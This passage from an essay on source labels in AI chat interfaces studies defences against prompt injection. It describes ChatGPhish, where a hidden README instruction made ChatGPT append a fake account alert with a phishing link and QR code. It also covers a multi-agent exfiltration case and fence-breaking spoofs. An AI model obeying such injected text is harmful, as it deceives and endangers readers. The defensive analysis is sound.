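FENCE python        meant to open an inner block, but read as plain text
An example
FENCE               meant to close the inner block, but closes the box
More quoted text    now outside the box
FENCE               meant to close the box, but opens a new one
```

The author can prevent this by using a longer fence for the outer box, such as four backticks.

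Lee and Kang (2026), in *LatentMD*, measured how often models break the boundaries of fenced blocks. They wrote 4,179 prompts, most of which asked for a Markdown document about a programming task, and gave them to nine models. The prompts varied in whether the model had to put its whole answer in a fence and in how many fenced blocks the answer should contain. In the main experiment, 38 percent of 19,128 usable answers had the right content but broken boundaries.

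The outer fence caused most of the failures. When the prompt required an outer fence, 95.5 percent of answers had a broken boundary, compared with 8.1 percent when the model followed an instruction not to use one. In a separate test, advice to use at least four backticks reduced failures from 96 to 65 percent. Of seven newer models, six still failed at least 96 percent of the time when they had to use an outer fence, while the seventh, Claude Sonnet 5, failed 34.7 percent of the time. A more lenient renderer wouldn't help much, since the four that Lee and Kang tried produced almost the same errors.

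Ordinary requests rarely create these conditions. Lee and Kang collected 248 real requests for Markdown documents from public chat logs, and the 16 models they tested broke a boundary in only about 2 percent of their answers. The rate was 17.5 percent when a model wrapped its whole answer in a fence and 0.8 percent when it didn't. A chat program that marked quotations with fences would make wrapping routine, but most web pages contain no fences of their own to conflict with the outer ones.

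However, an attacker can put a bare fence in the hidden text on purpose. If the model copies it exactly, the box closes there, and whatever the attacker wrote next looks like the assistant's own words. Lee and Kang studied accidental cases, so their figures don't show how often this attack would work.

JSON, a data format that uses different characters to open and close a group, stayed intact in every test. A provider could therefore have the model write its answer in JSON, with a field for the source of each passage, and software could reliably find where each passage ends. But the model would fill in the source field, so hidden text could influence what it puts there.

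### Recording sources outside the model

Software outside the model can keep a more dependable record. Google DeepMind's CaMeL and Microsoft's FIDES, both from 2025, do this. They are designed to stop agents from taking harmful actions, but a display could use the same records.

CaMeL divides the work between two models. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains that one of them reads only the user's request and writes a short program to carry it out. The other reads outside material but can't use any tools. For the bicycle review, the program might be:

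```
page = fetch("https://bikes.example/review")
summary = ask_second_model("Summarize this review", page)
show("Here is a summary of the review:")
show(summary)
```

The planning model never reads the page or the summary. Separate software runs the program and attaches a label to every value in it. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) describes a CaMeL label as a list of the sources that influenced the value and a list of who may read it. Here the summary's label would include `bikes.example` as a source, while the introductory line's label would list no outside source.

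A chat program could show the introductory line as the assistant's own text and put the summary in a box with its source. If the program renders the two separately, a fence in the review can't close the box, because the program doesn't search the text for a mark to find where the summary ends.

Hidden text can still change what is in the box. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) explains that an injection can't direct the planning model but can alter the value that the second model returns, so the summary could still recommend Northside Cycles. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) criticizes the system for not inspecting the final output, which means a summary could pass a planted instruction on to a human reader. The label would correctly name the page but wouldn't show that the page contained an instruction.

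FIDES labels every message and tool result. When a model reads several of them, its reply gets the combined label of them all, since software can't trace exactly what the model used. Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, define the combination in terms of possible writers *W* and permitted readers *R*. For a reply based on *n* items,

$$W = W_1 \cup \dots \cup W_n, \qquad R = R_1 \cap \dots \cap R_n$$

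Anyone who could have written any of the items may have influenced the reply, and only people allowed to read all of the items are allowed to read the reply.

The list of readers could help the renderer block leaks. Costa and colleagues check labels just before tool calls and treat a reply to the user as having no consequences. A reply with a remote image does have consequences, but their design also allows a check before the reply. A chat program could treat the owner of `pictures.example` as a reader of any image address on that server. It would then block an address that the model had composed with the user's heart condition in its context.

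### How precise the labels are, and what they cost

Combined labels quickly become vague. Suppose an assistant reads ten reviews and writes 20 sentences, each based on one review. Every sentence is labeled with all ten sources, so 180 of the 200 labels are unnecessary. *Sightline* calls this label creep. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* suggests replacing yes-or-no labels with estimates of how much information each source contributed. These would suit a display better but would no longer give a guarantee.

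CaMeL and FIDES both limit label creep by keeping outside text away from the planning model, which makes some tasks harder. Costa and colleagues measured this effect on AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks. An ordinary agent running GPT-4o completed 84 percent of tasks, averaged over the four settings. FIDES completed 61 percent with its security rules off and 50 percent with them on. A display that only needs labels could leave the rules off, so the drop from 84 to 61 percent is the closer estimate for it. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger model, that drop shrank from about 24 points to 6.3, and models have improved a great deal since.

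The provider could also add labels to an ordinary agent, which should still be able to do all the tasks it could do before. But after the agent had read one web page, everything it wrote would carry that page's label, including the sentence about comfort and weight.

Labels showing where text came from can be lost when agents work together. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) connected three CaMeL agents and asked them to send a colleague a summary of job applicants on Slack. The applicant database contained a planted instruction to email the details to an outside address. The coordinating agent put the summary into its request to the messaging agent, which treated the whole request as coming from its user and sent the email too. In a chat program, the same mistake could present an outsider's text as the assistant's own. The researchers fixed the agents' mistake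 by passing instructions and outside data through separate channels, which preserves the labels. The agents then completed fewer tasks, but the loss was modest for the strongest models.

Even an accurate label doesn't show how the model used a source. *Ghost in the Agent* (2026) points out that FIDES treats any path from a source to an action as strong evidence of influence, without showing whether the model reworded the source or only let it affect a decision. A chat program can recover some of this information by comparing each passage with the sources on its label, which takes much less searching than checking the whole context. A close match is probably copied. Without a match, the passage may be a fair paraphrase or an advertisement for Northside Cycles, and this comparison can't distinguish between them.

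## Showing readers where content came from

A source label in a chat interface shows readers where a piece of content came from. A chat program can often identify the source of copied text and loaded pictures, but it also has to put the label where readers will notice it and an attacker can't forge it. In spring 2026, ChatGPT's summaries of web pages had no such labels, and a security firm inserted false account alerts into them.

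### ChatGPhish

Permiso's researchers added an instruction to the end of a README, the page that introduces a software project on GitHub. The instruction required every summary to have two parts, a normal summary and a line about the reader's account. The researchers then opened the page in Firefox, which can pass a page's text to ChatGPT, and asked for a summary.

ChatGPT summarized the project as usual. Directly below, in the same style, it reported a new device on the reader's account (Chrome on Linux, in Pristina) and gave a link marked "Click here". The device didn't exist, and the link led to a website the researchers had chosen. A phishing email with the same text would have to get past a spam filter and then convince someone who hadn't asked for it, whereas this alert appeared on OpenAI's own website, in an answer the reader had requested.

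Another version put a QR code under the alert, which loaded automatically as a picture from Amazon storage that the researchers controlled. Someone on a desktop can hover over a link to see its address, and a company's security software may block the link, but neither protection helps a person who scans the code with a phone. A password manager on the phone should still refuse to fill in a password on the wrong website. Permiso also tried a picture behind a link shortener, which worked as a tracking pixel each time the answer appeared.

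The attack also worked from an ordinary web page about Kosovo, so GitHub wasn't the cause. Permiso doesn't blame Firefox either, because the browser only passed on the page's text. The Hacker News names Andi Ahmeti as the researcher and says Permiso had steered Microsoft Copilot's email summaries in a similar way that March.

Permiso gives this timeline for its dealings with OpenAI in 2026:

- 29 April: Permiso reported the problem through Bugcrowd.
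- 30 April: OpenAI marked the report "Not Reproducible" because it lacked detail.
- 1 May: Permiso sent a new version with fuller steps and screenshots. OpenAI classified it as "Not Applicable", and later as a duplicate of an earlier report.
- 7 May: Permiso asked to discuss the wider impact.
- 29 May: Permiso published its findings.

The last classification suggests that OpenAI already knew about the problem, and Permiso doesn't mention a fix. The title of its first report also mentions cross-site scripting (running an attacker's script in the page) and data exfiltration, but the published demonstrations show neither a script running nor conversation text being sent out.

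It is odd that the pictures loaded, because OpenAI had described its check against a public index four months before Permiso published, and a QR code made for a security test is unlikely to have been in that index. Permiso doesn't establish why they loaded. The check may not have covered page summaries. Or, since Firefox sends the page's text along with the reader's request, ChatGPT may have treated every address on the page as one the reader had supplied, and the older url_safe check accepted those. Either way, the addresses contained no private text, so OpenAI's narrower promise about leaks through the address still held.

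### The line of death

Browser makers faced the same problem much earlier. A web page's author can draw anything on the page, including a perfect copy of the browser's own warnings. Browsers therefore keep trustworthy indicators, such as the site's address, in a strip at the top of the window where the page can't draw. In *The Line of Death*, Lawrence (2017) gives the strip's lower edge that name. In theory, someone who trusts only what is above the line is safe. Chromium is the software behind Google's Chrome, and its developer guidance, *Security Considerations for Browser UI*, recommends placing trustworthy notices above the line, or at least overlapping or attached to it.

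Lawrence's view is gloomier. The browser displays an icon and title above the line, but the page supplies both. The domain name is accurate, but people misread it. For example, `paypal-account.com` need not belong to PayPal. Below the line, a page can show a picture of a whole browser window, including a fake address bar. Lawrence recalls a financial company whose entire security department failed to recognize one, although the fake window looked like it came from an older version of Windows than the real one around it. Full-screen mode and nearly all phones have no safe strip. The Register's *Chrome dev explains how modern browsers make secure UI just about impossible* (2017), an article about his post, describes the line as receding every year.

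His closest parallel to a chatbot is Outlook.com, which displayed the notice "This message is from a trusted sender" inside the message area. Phishers began putting copies of the notice at the top of their own emails.

In *Why Phishing Works*, Dhamija, Tygar and Hearst (2006) tested how well people use such indicators. They showed 22 university students and staff 20 websites and asked which were fraudulent. Participants correctly judged an average of 11.6 of the 19 scored sites (seven real and 12 fake), compared with the 9.5 expected from guessing. The most convincing fake, a copy of a bank's website whose address had two v's in place of a w, fooled 20 of the 22 participants. A fake PayPal page that displayed an imitation address bar and padlock fooled 81 percent.

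The five participants who looked only at the page's content, and never at the browser's indicators, got the five lowest scores. Some who noticed the browser's padlock put more trust in padlocks inside the page, where anyone can draw one. The study was small and used a browser from 2005. But its participants knew they were looking for fakes, so people browsing normally would probably have done worse. Dhamija and colleagues conclude that browsers must warn people about unsafe sites as well as marking safe ones.

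A chatbot's answer is entirely below the line, and a genuine address above it can make a malicious answer look trustworthy. *A real ChatGPT page is being used to trick people* (Keverenge, October 2026) describes an attack that the security firm Huntress discovered. The attackers published a customized version of ChatGPT called "Plus 5.6", which sounds like a new model from OpenAI. It sent users to a fake security check that got them to run a Windows command, which could install malware with access to their files, screen, webcam and microphone. Users started on the real ChatGPT website, so checking the address bar at that point would not have warned them.

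### Five kinds of label and how to fake them

A provider has several ways to show readers what came from outside. Text in the answer can imitate each of them to some extent:

| What the program shows | How the answer could imitate it | What makes that harder |
|---|---|---|
| A link's destination | Use a false address as the link's text | Add the real domain in a style that Markdown can't produce |
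| A frame around copied text | Open a false quotation, or close a real one early | Draw the frame from the program's own records |
| The server's name on an image | Put a false caption below it | Show the real name in a fixed place outside the picture |
| System notices outside the answer | Copy their wording, as in ChatGPhish | Never show a real notice inside an answer |
| Reasoning and sources in separate panels | Add a false "Sources" list at the end | Build the real list from a record of pages the program fetched |

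Attackers won't want to forge all of these marks. An official-looking account notice is worth forging, but a frame that marks text as copied from outside makes the text less convincing. Attackers would rather avoid that frame, and they can do so by having the model reword their message. A provider should therefore keep marks of trust out of the model's answer and use labels there mainly as warnings.

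If an interface shows fetched pages and the model's reasoning in separate panels, the heading of the reasoning panel shouldn't suggest that anyone has checked its contents. The program can confirm which pages it fetched, but it can't verify the model's reasoning.

Chat providers have one advantage over browser makers because a web page can draw anything, while an answer in Markdown can contain only what the renderer supports, such as bold text, headings, tables and links. The provider can reserve a margin beside the answer for its own labels, where the model can't write. The line of death would then run down the side of the answer. Phones are too narrow for a margin, so the program could instead separate passages with a strip in a color that the answer can't use.

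Remote images weaken this arrangement because they can contain perfect copies of the labels. An image can't extend into the margin, but a reader may not know that real labels appear only there. Leaving remote images unloaded keeps them from showing false labels and also protects the reader's data. A live page in a sandboxed frame can display a false label too.

Lawrence's favorite idea for browsers was to give each website a mark different for every user, so that an attacker can't know what to copy. In a chat program, the reader could pick a small symbol to appear on every real account notice. The program would have to keep the symbol out of the model's context, or hidden text could cause the model to reproduce it. Readers would also have to notice when the symbol was missing, and they may not, given that the security department didn't notice the wrong version of Windows.

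In February 2026 OpenAI introduced "Elevated Risk" labels for certain features of ChatGPT, its Atlas browser and its coding tool Codex, but the labels don't appear in answers. For example, the settings screen where a developer gives Codex internet access shows the label with an explanation of what will change, what the risks are and when such access is appropriate. An answer can't display anything on a settings screen, so the label is hard to fake. But it applies to a feature as a whole, and it wouldn't have helped a reader tell the false alert in Permiso's test from the summary above it. OpenAI plans to remove the label from a feature once it considers the risk sufficiently reduced.

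### Do labels change what readers believe?

Most research on AI answers concerns citations, the source labels people see most often. In *Citations and Trust in LLM Generated Answers*, Ding, Facciani and colleagues (2025) had 303 people ask a chatbot ten questions each and rate their trust in every answer from 1 to 10. Answers came with zero, one or five citations, depending on the group. Some participants got relevant links, while others got random links from other people's questions.

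Average trust was 7.73 with no citations, 8.10 with one and 8.17 with five. According to the paper's summary, even random citations raised trust, but its figures support this only weakly. In the statistical model, a citation raised trust by 0.394 points, but this gain was 0.268 smaller if the citation was random, leaving about 0.13. The 0.394 and 0.268 estimates each have a standard error of about 0.09, so the remaining gain could easily be due to chance.

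Li and Aral (2025) provide better evidence in *Human Trust in AI Search*. They showed 4,927 people, representative of US adults, Google's AI answers to nine questions on subjects such as gun control and vaccines. Adding reference links raised both trust and willingness to share the answer. The effect was the same whether the links were valid, broken or invented.

In Ding and colleagues' study, participants reported lower trust in answers when they had checked a citation. When they had checked a random citation, their average trust was 7.55, not significantly different from the score for answers with no citations. This doesn't prove that checking lowered trust, because people who already doubted an answer may have been more likely to check. Participants rarely checked, moving the mouse over a citation in only 193 of the 1,976 answers that had one, or about 10 percent.

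A source label could therefore backfire. If the false alert carried a small tag with GitHub's name, some readers might believe it more because the answer appeared to have a source. The label also has to make clear that the alert didn't come from the chat service.

More detailed labels can make readers warier. *PaperTrail* (Martin-Boyle, Leckey et al., 2026) describes an interface that splits an answer into claims, matches each with evidence from research papers, and flags claims that have none. In a test, 26 NASA researchers edited AI-written texts about Mars exploration, once with this interface and once with ordinary source citations. Trust in the model fell from 4.22 to 3.68 on a seven-point scale.

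But the researchers relied on the model's text as much as before. Martin-Boyle and colleagues measured reliance as

$$1 - \frac{d}{\max(m, n)}$$

where *d* is the smallest number of word changes that turns the model's draft into the participant's final text, and *m* and *n* are the lengths of the two texts, leaving out very common words. A score of 1 means that the participant changed nothing. The average was 0.73 with ordinary citations and 0.75 with the new interface, a difference that wasn't significant. With only 26 people, the study could have missed a modest effect. The measure also counts every edit equally, so it can't show whether people corrected the sentences that were wrong. Participants did find the new interface harder to use, and some thought it was cluttered.

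Neither Ding and colleagues nor Martin-Boyle and colleagues tested malicious content. A study that did is Li, Dai and colleagues (2026), in *Are You Sure?*, in which 303 people worked with AI agents that an attacker had manipulated. In one task, a hidden note in a résumé influenced the agent's choice of job candidate. In another, a false citation disabled the search tool. Participants got one of three kinds of warning, and afterwards the researchers asked whether they had noticed anything unusual:

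| Warning | Noticed something unusual |
|---|---|
| A disclaimer at the start | 8.6% |
| A reminder beside every answer | 20.0% |
| An alert that interrupts the task | 25.0% |

Of the three warnings, the reminder is the closest to a source label, and four out of five people who had it still missed the attack. "Unsure" counted as noticing, so even these figures may overstate how many people noticed. Because every task contained an attack, the study can't show how often people would have suspected an answer without one. The paper also gives inconsistent group sizes, with about 100 people per warning in one place and 183, 60 and 60 in another, so small differences between the groups don't mean much.

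The interrupting alert worked much better where people could easily check the result. It raised the share who noticed the attack from 9.8 to 50 percent for web searches, but only from 7.9 to 15 percent for travel bookings. This favors labels that let readers judge at a glance, such as one showing a link's real destination, over labels that require them to compare two documents. Li and colleagues also found that people who missed an attack often trusted the agent more after seeing warnings, because they took the warnings as a sign of a careful system.

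Nobody seems to have tested source labels on answers that hidden text has altered. An experiment would be fairly easy to run. It could show readers Permiso's false alert with and without labels, along with honest summaries to count false alarms. It should run for several weeks, since *Disclosure By Design* (2026) warns that people pay less attention to interface indicators as they get used to them.

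### The ChatGPhish answer with labels

Here is a simplified version of Permiso's answer, with invented addresses and a margin that only the chat program can write in:

```
ANSWER                             MARGIN
This project resizes photographs   Written after reading
and removes duplicates.            project.example

Account: A new device was added    Copied from project.example.
to your account: Chrome on Linux.  Not a notice from this service.

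Click here                         Opens login-check.example
                                   (not run by this service)

[picture not loaded]               From pictures.example
                                   (not run by this service)
```

The program can produce all of these labels without judging whether the page is hostile. The eight words "A new device was added to your account" also appear on the page, so a simple search for copied text would find them. The program can read the addresses of the link and the picture from their codes and check them against the provider's domains. A reader who looks at the margin would learn that the alert came from the page and that the link leads somewhere else. The picture stays unloaded because labeling it after it loads would be too late to prevent the tracking.

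If the reader loads the picture, the margin shows the server it came from but not the website the QR code opens. The program could easily decode the QR code and show that address too. A shortened link would be harder to trace, because the program would have to contact the shortening service to find out where the link leads.

The easiest way for the attacker to get around the margin is to have the model write the alert in its own words. A search for copied text would miss "Someone has signed in to your account from an unfamiliar computer", so the program could only label it "Written after reading project.example", the same label it gives the honest summary. The attacker can also leave out the link and the picture and ask the reader to call a phone number, so that the program has no web address to label.

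Lookalike addresses would still deceive some people. The note that a site is "not run by this service" exposes an imitation of the chat provider's own login page, but not one of the reader's bank, since the program usually can't identify the bank's domains. *Deceit and Deception*, a large study of phishing, found that an address such as `www-wellsfargo.com` could still get high ratings for authenticity if it matched the page's content.

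An accurate source label can also leave the reader deceived. In *Unsafe LLM-Based Search* (2025), researchers set up a phishing site that claimed to be the only reliable source on an organization and warned readers against the organization's official site. They then asked the search assistant Perplexity about it, using eight models. With every model, Perplexity presented the phishing site as authentic and attached a warning to the official one. A source label on those answers would have correctly identified the phishing site, but a reader who had never heard of the organization would have had no reason to doubt it.
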